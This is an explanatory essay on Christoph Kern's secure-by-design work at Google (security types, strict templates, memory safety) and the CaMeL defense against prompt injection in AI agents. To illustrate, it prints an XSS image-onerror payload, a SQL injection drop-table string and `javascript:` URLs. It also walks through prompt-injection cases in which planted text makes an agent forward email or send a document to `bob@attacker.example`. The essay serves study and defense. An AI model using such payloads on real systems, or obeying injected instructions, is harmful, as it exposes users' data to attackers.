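# Christoph Kern on secure-by-design software and prompt injection

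## Kern's work and the problem of data treated as instructions

Christoph Kern, a security engineer at Google, works mainly on preventing whole classes of software flaws through the design of programming languages, libraries and frameworks, so that security does not depend on every programmer avoiding every flaw. In 2025 Kern co-authored two papers on securing AI agents. One introduced CaMeL, a defense against an attack called prompt injection, and the other described Google's approach to agent security. The software flaws and prompt injection both arise because a system carries out part of a stranger's text as instructions when it should handle that text only as data.

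Kern has worked at Google since 2003 and in 2012 began leading a team that prevents vulnerabilities through the design of frameworks, platforms and APIs (the functions that one piece of software offers to another), according to the speaker's note for Kern's *Preventing Security Bugs through Software Design* (2015), a talk for the computing association USENIX. Before that, in 2007, Kern wrote the textbook *Foundations of Security* with Daswani and Kesavan. A profile page, Google Research's *Christoph Kern*, gives the current title as Principal Software Engineer. Kern is the sole author of most of the software articles, while the AI papers are joint work. The main publications are:

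- 2014: *Securing the Tangled Web*, an article by Kern on keeping attackers' scripts out of web pages.
- 2021: *If It's Not Secure, It Should Not Compile*, a conference paper with Pei Wang and Julian Bangert on applying the same ideas across Google's code.
- 2024: *Secure by Design: Google's Perspective on Memory Safety*, a joint paper on flaws in how programs use memory.
- June 2024: *Developer Ecosystems for Software Safety*, Kern's general argument that the tools and libraries developers work with determine how many flaws they introduce.
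- 2025: *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*, the CaMeL paper, by Edoardo Debenedetti and nine co-authors, Kern among them.
- May 2025: *Google's Approach for Secure AI Agents*, a white paper by Santiago Díaz, Kern and Kara Olive.
- Autumn 2025: *Safe Coding*, Kern's most rigorous statement of the method, first in the magazine ACM Queue and then, in November, as a longer technical report.

The newest dated entries on Google Research's page are from 2025. *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (2026), by other researchers, cites the CaMeL paper.

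### How an album title can run as a program

Untrusted data is any text that an attacker may have written, such as a form entry, an email or a web page. An injection vulnerability is a flaw that makes a program treat untrusted data as code or commands.

Kern explains the problem in *Securing the Tangled Web* with an imaginary photo-sharing site. When one user invites another to view an album, the site shows the invited user a notification containing the album's title. The site's code builds this notification by inserting the title between strings of HTML, the markup language of web pages. It then assigns the result to a property of the page called `innerHTML`, whose contents the browser interprets as markup.

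A title like "Lisbon in May" is harmless, but the person who sends the invitation chooses the title, and markup can carry scripts. A malicious user might call the album `<img src="x" onerror="stealPhotos()">`. This HTML makes the browser try to load an image from the address "x" and run a script if the loading fails, which it will. The string the browser receives doesn't mark which characters came from the site's programmers and which came from the user who typed the title. So the browser runs the script in the victim's session, with access to whatever the victim can see or change on the site.

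This kind of injection vulnerability, which lets an attacker's script run in another user's web session, is called cross-site scripting (XSS). In SQL injection, untrusted data changes the meaning of a database query written in SQL, a query language many databases use, and the attacker can then read or alter records they shouldn't have access to.

The album bug has a short fix, which is to HTML-escape the title. Escaping replaces characters that have a special meaning in markup with codes for those characters, so `<` becomes `&lt;`. The browser then displays the whole title as text in the victim's notification and doesn't create an image or run the script.

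### The case for training, review and testing

The album bug is easy to understand, which is a good argument for the usual way of dealing with such bugs. An organization teaches its developers the escaping rules, has other engineers review the code, and runs automated scanners and tests. These tests include fuzzing, which feeds a program many unusual inputs to see what breaks. If the developer forgets to escape a title, the reviewer may notice, and if the reviewer misses it, the scanner may still detect it.

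This approach also works on code that already exists. Kern's alternative constrains how people write programs, and a company with millions of lines of old code may not be able to afford to rewrite them. In a 2024 podcast interview with OpenSSF, the Open Source Security Foundation, Kern assumed that most existing software in C++, an older language that leaves memory management largely to the programmer, would stay in C++ for the rest of its life. People will have to keep finding and fixing flaws in much of that code.

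Finding flaws has also become much easier. Google's *Stronger with every update* (2026) describes how the Chrome security team uses Gemini models to automate finding, triaging and patching vulnerabilities. A skeptic of Kern's program could reasonably ask why anyone should redesign their libraries if a model can read all the code and repair it.

Kern once gave the traditional advice too, as he wrote in the 2014 article. Its references for that advice include the 2007 textbook, subtitled *What Every Programmer Needs to Know*. In 2014 Kern still thought that inspection and testing had great value and might even find most of the bugs in an application.

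### Why finding many bugs is not enough

Kern objects that after reviewing and testing a large web application, a team has no good way to tell whether it found all the XSS bugs, or even nearly all of them. An attacker may need only one that the team missed.

Escaping untrusted text is difficult partly because the rules depend on where the text is used. Kern's photo site has another bug, in the code that runs after a user logs back in. The site returns the user to the page they were on before their session expired. It reads that page's address from a parameter in the current web address, which an attacker can set by luring the user to a prepared link. Browsers accept addresses that begin with `javascript:` and run the rest as a script. HTML-escaping doesn't prevent this, because the dangerous address need not contain any special HTML characters, so a developer who knew to escape the album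 title could still write the login bug. The code must instead check that the address starts with something harmless, such as `https`. Style sheets and scripts embedded in a page have further rules.

It is also hard to know where a value came from. To show that an application has no XSS, a reviewer has to find every sink, meaning every place where the program passes a string to something that will interpret it. From each sink that lacks a check, the reviewer traces the value backward until it is clear that the application fully controls it, that earlier code made it safe, or that there is a bug. For the album title, this trail runs from the browser code to the web server, then to the database, and finally to a different user who typed the title earlier. The same database also holds values that the site's staff configured, so a reviewer cannot tell whether a string is safe just from knowing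 that it came from storage.

Kern's user profile example shows how people can make mistakes at such a boundary. Users of the photo site may write an "about me" text with colors and links, so the developers turn off escaping for that field. The browser editor produces only harmless markup, but an attacker can tamper with the browser-side program and send the server any markup, which the server does not check. Kern suggests that a bug like this could arise because the front-end and back-end developers misunderstood who was responsible for the check. A reviewer who looked at only one side might well make the same mistake.

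Automated scanners have similar problems. Kern writes that at Google, tools that analyze code without running it raised false alarms, missed real bugs, and worked poorly when data crossed between programming languages, servers and stored records. Many are also too slow to run before a developer's change enters the shared code. In *Developer Ecosystems for Software Safety*, Kern points out that later scans can help remove bugs but do not slow the rate at which developers add new ones.

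The same article extends the argument beyond injection. In its example, a developer notices that a C++ program never releases certain memory, and adds a statement to release it. The program still uses that memory elsewhere, in code the developer did not change and may never have seen. The official coding rule against accessing freed memory is correct, but it would not have helped, because the developer believed that nothing was still using the memory.

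The problem gets worse as the opportunities for error multiply. Kern writes that a large web application can have hundreds of places that pass data to a sink, and that one omission can compromise the whole application. If, for example, an application has 500 such places, and developers independently handle each one correctly 99.9% of the time, the chance that all 500 are right is 0.999 to the power of 500, or about 61%. Roughly two in five such applications would contain at least one hole.

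Kern also points out in *Safe Coding* that a test observes the program only on particular inputs, whereas safety is a claim about every possible execution, including those an attacker will look for. Kern cites the computer scientist Edsger Dijkstra's 1970 observation that testing can reveal bugs but never prove that there are none. Modern fuzzers choose their inputs much more cleverly than anyone could in 1970, but they still try only a sample.

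As evidence that the traditional approach fell short in practice, Kern often refers to the "Stubborn Weaknesses" list from the Common Weakness Enumeration, a public catalog of software flaws, where XSS and SQL injection ranked second and third in 2023. Such rankings show that the flaws persist across the industry, but they are weak evidence about how well training works, since many of the developers behind those flaws may have had no decent training. Google's own history is stronger evidence. The company had security specialists, reviews and tests, yet around 2014 it still tended to find tens of XSS vulnerabilities a year in each large application such as Gmail. However, this is the company's own account, and it has no comparison group.

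AI bug-finding came after most of Kern's argument and weakens some of it. If a model can trace every path from every sink with little effort, the labor of review matters less. The logical point still holds, because a search that finds no flaws doesn't prove there are none, however good the searcher. Whether the remaining risk justifies a redesign then depends on how much effort it takes to prevent the flaws.

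Kern concludes that organizations should stop blaming these flaws on individual carelessness. *Developer Ecosystems for Software Safety* describes the possibility of writing such a bug as a hazard of the development environment, and says the people who build that environment should remove the hazard. Kern calls this approach safe coding.

### From injected code to injected prompts

An AI agent is a system in which a language model plans and takes actions through tools such as email or file access. Suppose a user asks an agent to summarize the morning's email. The agent fetches the messages, and its software puts their text in the model's prompt, the text the model works from, alongside the user's request. In one of the messages, a stranger has written a line telling the assistant to forward all of the user's email to an outside address. If the model follows that line, the agent will send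 the user's private email to the attacker. The software developer Simon Willison uses a shorter version of this example in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (2025).

This is prompt injection, in which an attacker hides instructions in data that a language model reads, and the model follows them. Díaz and colleagues explain that it is possible because current language models do not rigorously separate the parts of a prompt. The white paper recommends that developers mark where the user's request ends and the email begins, but the model may not respect the marking. Agents that plan in a loop are more exposed, since they may take in new data at every step. An agent with a memory may even store the attacker's text as a supposed fact and act on it in a later, unrelated task, much as the album title sits in the database until the victim opens the notification.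 An attacker who controls an agent's output through prompt injection can also cause XSS if an application displays that output without escaping it.

Willison proposed the name in September 2022, in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3*. The day before, Riley Goodside had published examples in which GPT-3, an early OpenAI language model, was supposed to translate a passage into French. The passage contained an instruction to ignore those directions and produce a taunt instead, and the model followed it. Willison noticed that developers were building products on GPT-3 by writing their instructions, adding the user's text to the end, and sending the model the combined string.

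Programs vulnerable to SQL injection do the same thing. In Willison's example, a program writes `select * from users where username = '`, appends whatever name a visitor typed, and adds a closing quotation mark. A visitor who types `'; drop table users;` ends the name early and adds a command that deletes the table of users. Willison named prompt injection after SQL injection because in both cases the programmer has joined trusted and untrusted text into one string.

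Willison later found that people unfamiliar with SQL injection took "prompt injection" to mean typing a malicious prompt into a chatbot. That is jailbreaking, where the user tries to get around the model's own restrictions. In the email example, by contrast, the user is the victim. Four days after proposing the name, Willison wrote in *I don't know how to solve prompt injection* (2022) that XSS and SQL injection had known solutions, but that there seemed to be no reliable way to beat prompt injection.

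## Safe coding: making a class of flaws impossible to write

The known solution to SQL injection is to give the database the query and the user's data separately. The programmer writes a query with a placeholder, such as `where username = ?`, and supplies the name as a value that the database never reads as part of the command. Security guides widely recommend this practice, called parameter binding, but programmers sometimes forget it. Under Kern's safe coding, code with this mistake does not compile, so no one can run it.

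### Enclosing the risky operations

Kern calls an operation risky if it is safe only under a condition that the programmer has to ensure, known as a safety precondition. For example, reading item `i` of an array in C is safe only if the array has an item `i`. Running a database query is safe only if no part of its text came from an attacker.

The risk spreads to other code. In one of Kern's examples, a function called `getWidgetsBy` pastes its argument into a query and runs the query. Calling it with untrusted data causes an SQL injection, so `getWidgetsBy` is risky too, and so is any function that passes its own argument to it. To show that this one query is safe, a reviewer would have to follow all of these calls through the program.

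Safe coding stops the spread by placing every risky operation inside a safe abstraction, a module that other code can call in any way without causing the flaw. The module itself ensures that every precondition holds. Sometimes a runtime check is enough. Arrays in Java, Go and Rust carry their own length, and the program compares the index with that length before it accesses the memory. An out-of-bounds index causes an ordinary error, which may still crash the program but doesn't let an attacker run code.

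No such check exists for a query, because a joined string, like the album notification, contains no record of which parts the programmer wrote. Kern therefore records that information in the string's type, the label that determines what a program may do with a value. A security type is a type whose values are all safe for a stated use.

### A query function that accepts no ordinary strings

Because a "safely constructed" query is hard to define exactly, Kern instead requires every piece of the query to come from the developers, a stricter condition that tools can check. The pieces are usually literals, the quoted strings in the program's own source code. Google represents such queries with a security type called `TrustedSqlString`, a thin wrapper around a string. Very few functions can create values of this type. Developers assemble the query with a builder whose append function accepts literals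 but not arbitrary strings.

The query function changes too, so that it accepts only a `TrustedSqlString`. Suppose a developer wants to list one user's photo albums, and `name` holds whatever a visitor typed. In simplified code, the unsafe attempt looks like this:

```
q.append("SELECT title FROM albums WHERE owner = ")
q.append(name)              // error: name is not a literal
db.query(q.build())
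```

The compiler rejects the second line. Joining the strings first and passing the result straight to `db.query` doesn't work either, because the result is an ordinary string. This version compiles:

```
q.append("SELECT title FROM albums WHERE owner = ?")
db.query(q.build(), name)
```

If the visitor types `'; drop table users;`, the database now looks for a user with that strange name and finds no albums.

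The guarantee follows by induction. An empty query contains no untrusted data, and appending a literal to a query without untrusted data doesn't add any. So no sequence of appends can produce a `TrustedSqlString` that contains something the visitor typed.

### User text in web pages

Literals are not enough for web pages, which have to display text that users wrote. For most of this text, including the album title in Kern's XSS example, developers can use a template, a page with gaps for values to fill. Google's template systems work out whether each gap is in ordinary text, a link, a style sheet or a script, and apply the escaping or checks required there. The strict version described in *Securing the Tangled Web* doesn't let developers turn this off.

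That rule causes a problem for the photo site's "about me" field, because escaping would display the users' markup as raw code. So the developers give the field the type `SafeHtml`, whose values cannot run an attacker's script when a browser displays them as HTML. The template inserts `SafeHtml` values unchanged and escapes everything else. On the server, a sanitizer strips the user's text of anything that could run a script, and the program then converts the result to `SafeHtml`.

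This last step, which Kern calls an unchecked conversion, is risky because it turns any string into `SafeHtml` without examining it. A security expert therefore reviews every use. The photo site needs only one, in the same package as the sanitizer. If the back-end developers forget to call the sanitizer, they have an ordinary string where the program requires `SafeHtml`, and the code doesn't compile.

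A page can usually link to a stranger's website safely, but not load a script from it. Google therefore uses the type `SafeUrl` for addresses that users may follow and the type `TrustedResourceUrl` for addresses that a page may load code from.

### Banning the raw operations

None of this helps if developers can still assign a string to `innerHTML`, the browser property in the album bug. *If It's Not Secure, It Should Not Compile*, a 2021 paper by Wang, Bangert and Kern, describes how Google changed its compilers for JavaScript and TypeScript, the main languages of browser code, to reject such assignments. The check deliberately doesn't try to work out whether a particular string is dangerous, so it is fast enough to run in every build. When the compiler rejects code, it tries to suggest a fix that uses the safe alternative.

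Experts keep a central list of files that may use the raw operations, and a developer who needs an exception must ask them to review the code. In *Secure by Design* (2024), Kern and a Google colleague, Alex Rebert, argue that these rules have to be compulsory. They write that too many risky operations remained in the code when safe abstractions were optional, and that without mandatory review, developers made many unchecked conversions that were unnecessary or unsound.

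### Why a reviewer can read one module

Safe coding's central argument comes from formal verification, the practice of proving mathematically that a program meets a specification. Let *T*(*q*) mean that developers wrote every piece of the query *q*. The raw query operation has the precondition *T*(*q*). If *q* is an ordinary string, every function that passes it along needs the same precondition, and someone has to show that *T*(*q*) holds at each call.

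With the security type, the claim becomes that *T*(*w*) holds for every value *w* of type `TrustedSqlString`. Whether this is true depends only on the code that can create or change such values, all of which is in one module. An expert reads that module and confirms the induction. For the rest of the program, the compiler's ordinary type checking confirms that each call to the query function supplies a value of the right type. Thousands of developers can then change the application every day without anyone repeating the expert's work.

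The reviewer has to read the whole module, since code far from the risky line may break the property that the line depends on. Kern admits that experts usually check these modules by careful informal reasoning, without a formal proof. He also notes that Java's reflection feature lets code change another module's private data, and that TypeScript lets a programmer relabel a value as a different type. Safe coding therefore makes a flaw impossible to write only in code that avoids such features.

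### Invariants and the developer ecosystem

In *Secure by Design at Google*, Kern (2024) extends the argument from particular libraries to the way organizations make software. He recommends stating security goals as invariants, properties that a system must keep in every possible state, even under attack. For SQL injection, the invariant is that wherever the code runs a query, in any state the program can reach and with any input from outside, the query must consist only of trustworthy pieces, with untrusted values supplied separately.

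Training and review can miss a case, so the word "every" rules out relying on them. Kern compares a design that depends on people's care to an extension cord with a plug at both ends. Anyone who plugs one end into the wall before connecting the other is holding live prongs, and a warning label would do little to prevent that. Manufacturers prevent the accident by putting a socket on one end.

The same reasoning applies to flaws that don't involve strings. Suppose every request to a web service must pass a permission check. If each function in the service performs its own check, one omission breaks the invariant, and a reviewer has to reread every function for each release. If the framework instead checks each request before it reaches any function, the reviewer only has to read the framework.

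*Developer Ecosystems for Software Safety* generalizes this, arguing that a product's security is largely an emergent property of the developer ecosystem, which includes the languages, libraries, frameworks, build tools and systems that engineers use to put software into operation. That is, the rate of flaws depends more on how these fit together than on how careful any one developer is. For example, engineers who configure servers by hand will sometimes change the wrong machine. Google keeps many of these settings in files, where a second person and automatic checks can examine a change before it takes effect.

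The thesis is plausible for mistakes that thousands of developers could all make, but less useful for flaws that depend on what a particular product is for. Kern accepts that a banking app and a photo editor face different threats, and a shared framework can't determine who should be allowed to approve a bank transfer.

### Memory safety

Memory errors are the second large test of the method. Rebert and Kern report that these errors cause about 70% of severe vulnerabilities in large C and C++ programs. The problem has the same structure as injection, since using a pointer, a value that holds a memory address, is a risky operation whose precondition is that the address still belongs to the right object. But a C++ program contains so many of these operations that a library can't enclose them all, so the language itself has to be the safe abstraction.

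How hard this is depends on the kind of error. To prevent access beyond the end of an array, the program can store the array's length and check it with little overhead. Use-after-free errors, in which a program uses memory it has already released, are much harder to prevent because a program has no quick way to check whether other pointers to an object still exist when it releases that object. Java and Go avoid the problem by releasing memory automatically once nothing refers to it, which takes time while the program runs. Rust instead requires programmers to structure their code so that the compiler can prove that no reference outlives its object. This adds no work at run time, but the code takes more effort to write.

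C++ generally has neither mechanism, and Rebert and Kern see "no realistic path" for it to become rigorously memory-safe. They also think rewriting Google's hundreds of millions of lines of C++ will probably remain impractical. They therefore recommend memory-safe languages for new code and for components at particular risk, while making the remaining C++ safer where possible. One partial measure is memory tagging, in which the processor gives each pointer and each region of memory one of 16 tags and stops the program if a pointer's tag doesn't match the tag of the memory it is used to access. With random tags, an outdated pointer still has a 1 in 16 chance of matching.

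Rust also needs exceptions to its safety rules, for instance to communicate with hardware. Programmers have to mark this code with the word `unsafe`, which shows reviewers where to look, much as unchecked conversions do.

### What happened at Google

The earliest figures come from two large Google applications. *Securing the Tangled Web* reports that developers filed 31 XSS bugs against the first in 2012. The team moved to strict templates in early 2013, and the count fell to four in the year to mid-2014, all in the first six months of that period. A second application, which was still migrating, went from 21 bugs to nine over the same period. Kern called these observations anecdotal, since the size of the code and the training of its developers may also have changed.

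The 2021 paper covers DOM-based XSS, the kind that arises in browser code. One product had ten such vulnerabilities in the year before it adopted the new rules, two in the year of adoption and one in the year after. These are small numbers from a single team that volunteered early. After the rollout began in 2018, DOM-based XSS also made up a falling share of the serious vulnerabilities that outsiders reported across the company.

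Wang and colleagues' more informative finding is that a growing proportion of the remaining bugs came from old code exempt from the rules, even though the amount of exempt code was shrinking. Safer browsers alone would not easily explain this pattern, because they should have benefited both old and new code. Better training could still explain part of it, because training affects only code that people write afterward, and Google ran a campaign to promote the safe functions in October 2018.

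By 2025, according to Kern, hundreds of web applications built on the hardened frameworks together averaged less than one XSS report a year, when a single large application used to have tens. Google Photos, which used such a framework from the start, has never had an XSS report. Applications that use the safe database functions have had no reported SQL injection for more than a decade, although Kern doesn't give an earlier rate for comparison.

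For memory safety, the main evidence comes from Google's Android operating system. Around 2019 its developers began to favor memory-safe languages for new code. Memory errors then fell from 76% of Android's vulnerabilities in 2019 to 24% in 2024, and Vander Stoep (2025), in *Rust in Android*, puts the 2025 share below 20%. The number of memory-safety vulnerabilities had also fallen by 2022, according to an Android report that Rebert and Kern quote, so the share did not fall only because other kinds of flaws became more common.

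Vander Stoep also compares Rust directly with C and C++. Android had about five million lines of Rust and one potential memory-safety vulnerability in them, which the team fixed before release. The rate was 0.2 per million lines, compared with roughly 1,000 per million in Android's C and C++ code. An estimate based on one bug is very uncertain, and people have had much longer to find flaws in the older code. But if the Rust code contained a hundred times as many flaws as the team found, its rate would still be a fiftieth of the rate for C and C++.

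All of this evidence comes from Google, and none from a controlled experiment. It is mostly counts of reported flaws, which also depend on how hard people looked. I would be cautious about using it to estimate exactly how much safe coding contributed. But the decline in XSS was very large, lasted for years, and is what we would expect from how safe coding works, so training or chance alone is unlikely to explain it.

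### The cost of old code

Safe coding took little work to maintain at Google once the tools existed. The company had more than a million JavaScript files, and by the end of 2020 less than 1% of them had an exemption. During five months of the early rollout, the security team received fewer than eight requests for exceptions a week on average, while developers submitted around 10,000 JavaScript-related changes a week.

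Other organizations may find safe coding harder to adopt. Wang and colleagues say that Google benefited from keeping its code in one repository, compiling it with the same tools and requiring review of every change. Converting old code also takes a lot of work. The early product team, which had a few tens of engineers working on browser code, needed about a year to clean up most of its violations. Kern describes the initial investment for existing code as anything from modest to "very significant". To avoid stopping all other work, Google let old violations compile and removed them gradually.

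The alternative is to keep the old design and use AI to find its flaws. Anthropic's *Launching an opt-in vulnerability-finding service for open-source software* (2026) reports that language models found under 20% of the flaws in one benchmark at the start of 2025 and over 85% in 2026. By October, Anthropic's models had found more than 29,000 candidate vulnerabilities in important software, but the company's staff had reviewed only about 6,000 of them by hand.

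Repairs have been slower still. In November, the security company VulnCheck examined the public record of these findings and counted 37,966, of which 217 were marked as fixed (*After 7-months, Glasswing Overwelms Maintainers with Underwhelming Findings*, 2026). Since September, the record had gained nearly 12,000 findings but only 15 fixes.

People had not yet checked most of the findings, so dividing 217 by 37,966 would exaggerate the failure. Cornelißen (2026), in *Glasswing*, adds that the record covers only open-source software, so it omits flaws that companies such as Microsoft and Cisco find and quietly repair in their own products. A company that controls its code can probably fix it faster than volunteers can. Even so, the figures suggest that when flaws are easier to find, much of the work shifts to confirming and repairing them. Rebert and Kern noticed this in 2024, when an automated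 testing tool for the Linux kernel was already finding bugs faster than developers fixed them.

This makes prevention more attractive for new code, because nobody has to confirm or patch a flaw that never existed. AI may eventually reduce the work of finding and fixing flaws in old C++ by translating it into safer languages. Rebert (2026), in *Memory Safety at Scale*, suggests 2060 as a possible date for completing the move to memory safety, or 2035 if AI speeds up software work by 10 to 100 times. Rebert marks both dates with question marks, but the possibility of the earlier one means that the 2024 judgment about rewriting may not last.

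### The assumption of well-intentioned developers

Safe coding protects developers from their own mistakes but assumes they aren't trying to defeat it. In Kern's example of how they could, a programmer writes a table containing every character as a literal. A function then takes an attacker's string, looks up each character in the table and appends the matching literal to a query. Every append follows the rules, so the code compiles, but the finished `TrustedSqlString` contains exactly what the attacker typed.

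Kern says this hasn't been a significant problem at Google, where developers are trusted and such code would look obviously wrong to a reviewer. The method provides no assurance where developers may be malicious, as on a cloud service that runs strangers' programs.

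## CaMeL: a structural defense against prompt injection

CaMeL, short for "Capabilities for Machine Learning", aims to separate instructions from data in AI agents, much as parameter binding does in database queries. Edoardo Debenedetti introduced it in a March 2025 paper with Nicholas Carlini, Daniel Fabian, Tianqi Fan, Jamie Hayes, Kern, Chongyang Shi, Ilia Shumailov, Andreas Terzis and Florian Tramèr. They built on a pattern that Willison had proposed two years earlier, and they found a gap in it.

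### Two models, one of them without tools

In April 2023, Willison suggested dividing an assistant's work between two language models. A privileged model takes the user's request and can use tools, but never reads untrusted data. That data goes to a quarantined model, which has no tools. When the quarantined model summarizes an email, ordinary software stores the summary under a name such as `$email-summary-1`. The privileged model can then use that name to have the software display the summary, without seeing the text itself.

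If a stranger's email contains an instruction to forward the whole mailbox, the model that reads the email can't forward anything, and the instruction never reaches the model that can. This separation protects the agent's control flow (which actions run and in what order) but not its data flow (the values that pass from one action to another).

Debenedetti and colleagues showed the gap with a user who asks the agent to send Bob the document he requested in their last meeting. The user adds that Bob's email address and the name of the document are in the meeting notes. Suppose an attacker has managed to add a line to those notes, giving Bob's address as `bob@attacker.example`. Under Willison's pattern, the attack works like this:

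1. The privileged model plans to find the notes, extract the document's name and Bob's address, fetch the document and send it.
2. The software finds the notes and gives them to the quarantined model.
3. The quarantined model returns the name "Q3 budget" and the forged address, which the software stores as `$name` and `$address`.
4. The privileged model tells the software to fetch the document called `$name` and send it to `$address`. The attacker receives the budget.

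The agent took exactly the steps the user wanted, in the right order. The attacker only had to change one value.

### How CaMeL follows a value

CaMeL keeps the two models, but the privileged model now writes its whole plan as a short program before any untrusted data arrives. The program is in a restricted version of Python, which the authors chose because language models already write Python well. For Bob's document, a simplified plan looks like this:

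```
notes = find_notes("last meeting")
name = ask_quarantined("Which document did Bob ask for?", notes)
address = ask_quarantined("What is Bob's email address?", notes)
document = fetch_document(name)
send_email(recipient=address, attachment=document)
```

A custom interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the plan and attaches a tag called a capability to each value. As Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues explain in *CaMeLoT* (2026), the tag records where the value came from and who may read it. For example, the permitted readers of a private calendar event depend on the user and the people invited. When the interpreter computes one value from another, the new value inherits the old one's origins.

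Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a security policy, a small Python function that allows or denies the call after examining it, its arguments and their capabilities. The policy for changing a password, for instance, accepts only a password that came from the user. If an action isn't clearly safe, the system can ask the user to approve it.

With the same forged line in the notes, CaMeL proceeds as follows:

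1. The interpreter fetches the notes and tags them as untrusted, because other people can edit the file.
2. The quarantined model returns "Q3 budget" and the forged address. Both came from the notes, so the interpreter tags both as untrusted.
3. The interpreter fetches the budget, whose tag lists the people who may read it.
4. The policy for `send_email` requires a trusted recipient. The forged address came from the notes and isn't among the user's known contacts, so the interpreter stops and asks whether to send the budget to `bob@attacker.example`.

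The attacker fooled the quarantined model in both versions. Under CaMeL, the attack succeeds only if the user approves the strange address. But if Bob's real address also appears only in the notes, the user must approve it too, even when there is no attack.

The attacker could instead forge the name of the document, so that Bob receives a list of salaries. A policy that checks only the recipient would allow this if Bob is a known contact, but one that compares the recipient with the document's permitted readers would stop it. CaMeL's fixed plan protects the control flow without any policies, but how well CaMeL protects the data depends on how well the policies are written.

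The design can also help with privacy. Extracting an address is easier than planning, so the quarantined model could be small enough to run on the user's own device. The company that provides the privileged model would then see the request but not the notes.

### Falsehoods that break no rule

Suppose the user only wants a summary of the meeting, and the attacker's line in the notes says that the team agreed to cancel the project. The quarantined model includes this in its summary, and the user gets a false report. A capability can record where a sentence came from but not whether it is true, and no sensible policy forbids showing users a summary of their own notes.

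In *Operationalizing CaMeL*, Tallam and Miller (2025) describe a PDF that contains a line instructing the reader to forward the file to an outside address. The agent doesn't follow the instruction, but its summary may repeat it, and the user might then follow it. They propose using a language model to check the agent's output for suspicious text. That might help, but it brings back the model-based detection that CaMeL was supposed to make unnecessary.

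Sometimes a user deliberately lets a document decide what an agent does. In one test task, the user asks an agent to read a file and make the payment it describes, and the attacker replaces the file's contents with a different payment request. *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) treats this as a limit of every defense that tracks where data came from. Such a defense can block all payments based on the file, but it cannot distinguish the fraudulent one from the genuine ones.

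### Comparison with safe coding

The following comparison with safe coding is this writer's own. CaMeL's interpreter resembles one of Kern's safe abstractions because the plan can call tools in any way, and the interpreter must check that each call is safe. Capabilities resemble security types such as `TrustedSqlString` because both preserve information that an ordinary string loses.

Security types and CaMeL check values at different times and make different assumptions about who wrote them. A compiler enforces security types before the program runs, on the assumption that the developers who construct the values mean well. CaMeL's interpreter checks values while the plan runs and tags them by origin, which allows for values written by an attacker. In Kern's example, a program copies an attacker's string by looking up its characters in a table of literals, and the compiler accepts the copy.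 An interpreter that tracks dependencies properly would mark the copy as untrusted, because the attacker's string determined which characters the program looked up.

Because CaMeL checks at run time, a plan may fail halfway through, after the agent has already taken some actions. Its security also still depends on trusting the user's request, the interpreter, and whoever decides which sources count as trusted.

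### Results on AgentDojo

AgentDojo is a benchmark that measures how often agents finish tasks and how often prompt injections against them succeed. It has 97 user tasks involving office work, Slack messages, banking and travel. In tests with OpenAI's o3 model, CaMeL solved 77% of the tasks with what its authors call provable security, while an undefended agent solved 84%. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) reports the same figures.

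CaMeL also uses more computation. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025), a comparison of several defenses, reports that on the median task CaMeL used 2.82 times as many input tokens (the pieces of text a model processes) and 2.73 times as many output tokens as an undefended agent. This was the largest increase of any defense in the comparison.

CaMeL's original evaluation recorded two successful prompt injection attacks, according to Garby and colleagues. In one, the user had asked the agent to pay whatever a document said, which the CaMeL authors place outside the attacks they try to prevent. In the other, the agent merely quoted a hotel review containing text that the benchmark counts as a success for the attacker. *How to Stop an AI Agent From Being Fooled*, an article by Schmidt Sciences, one of the project's funders, therefore overstates the result when it credits CaMeL with fending off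 all known prompt injection attacks.

Later tests found a larger loss of usefulness. *SecureClaw* (2026), which introduces a competing defense, reports that none of 629 attacks succeeded against CaMeL, but CaMeL solved only 29 of the 97 tasks when there was no attack, while SecureClaw solved 59. The researchers had to adapt CaMeL's released code to their setup and had an interest in their own system doing well, so this result deserves some caution.

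Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL on the banking tasks with its policies switched off and then on. With OpenAI's GPT-5.2, it completed 32 of 48 runs without the policies and 18 with them. With MiMo-v2.5, the number fell from 34 to 18. The policies stopped every attack in the runs that finished, but only five of 622 attacks had succeeded without them, because in about two-thirds of the task-attack pairings the attack required an action that would never appear in the user's plan. In this test, the policies blocked many legitimate tasks to prevent a few attacks.

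This suggests that the original gap of seven percentage points is a poor estimate of how much CaMeL reduces task completion under strict policies. Outside a benchmark, though, the system could ask the user about some blocked actions and then continue the task. The policies are still useful, because an attacker who knew the design would target the data.

### Writing policies and asking users

The CaMeL paper says that prompt injection is not fully solved. Someone has to write the policies and keep them up to date, and users may get tired of approving actions. A user who has clicked "yes" on twenty harmless emails may not read the address on the next one. Willison worries about both problems, and admits that he still struggles with Amazon's cloud permission settings after two decades in application security.

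The first problem may be worse for a large company. Tallam and Miller warn that an organization with hundreds of tools could end up with duplicated and inconsistent policies. They suggest sorting actions by risk. The agent could list calendar events after a basic check, ask for a quick confirmation before moving a file, and require stronger approval to send an email or transfer money. This would mean fewer questions, but someone still has to decide which group each action belongs in.

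### Plans that cannot wait for the data

An ordinary agent can read an email, find that it needs another file, and fetch it, but CaMeL's privileged model has to plan for that file before anyone opens the email. It also needs the format of each tool's output in advance, because it writes a program to process output it will never see. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) reports that most of the CaMeL agents' task failures in its tests came from committing to a plan too early.

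Some tasks don't fit the design because their steps are in the untrusted data. In one of Garby and colleagues' runs without policies, the user asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The privileged model wrote a program that translated each instruction in the file into a tool call. This was a clever way to complete the task, but it let whoever wrote the file control the agent again.

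Computer use seems even harder. An agent that operates a normal desktop usually looks at the screen before each click, and the screen may contain an attacker's text. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) have the privileged model write a plan with branches for everything it expects might happen. A quarantined model that can read images answers questions about the screen, such as whether a cookie banner is visible, and the interpreter then picks a branch. These plans averaged about 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with roughly five calls and four branches for AgentDojo.

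On 109 tasks from OSWorld, a benchmark of everyday computer work, the version built on Claude Sonnet 4.5 completed 31 on the first attempt and 62 within five. The researchers describe this as keeping up to 57% of an undefended frontier agent's performance. This measure is optimistic because in practice someone would have to know which of the five attempts had worked. The system used 1.88 times as many tokens as the undefended agent.

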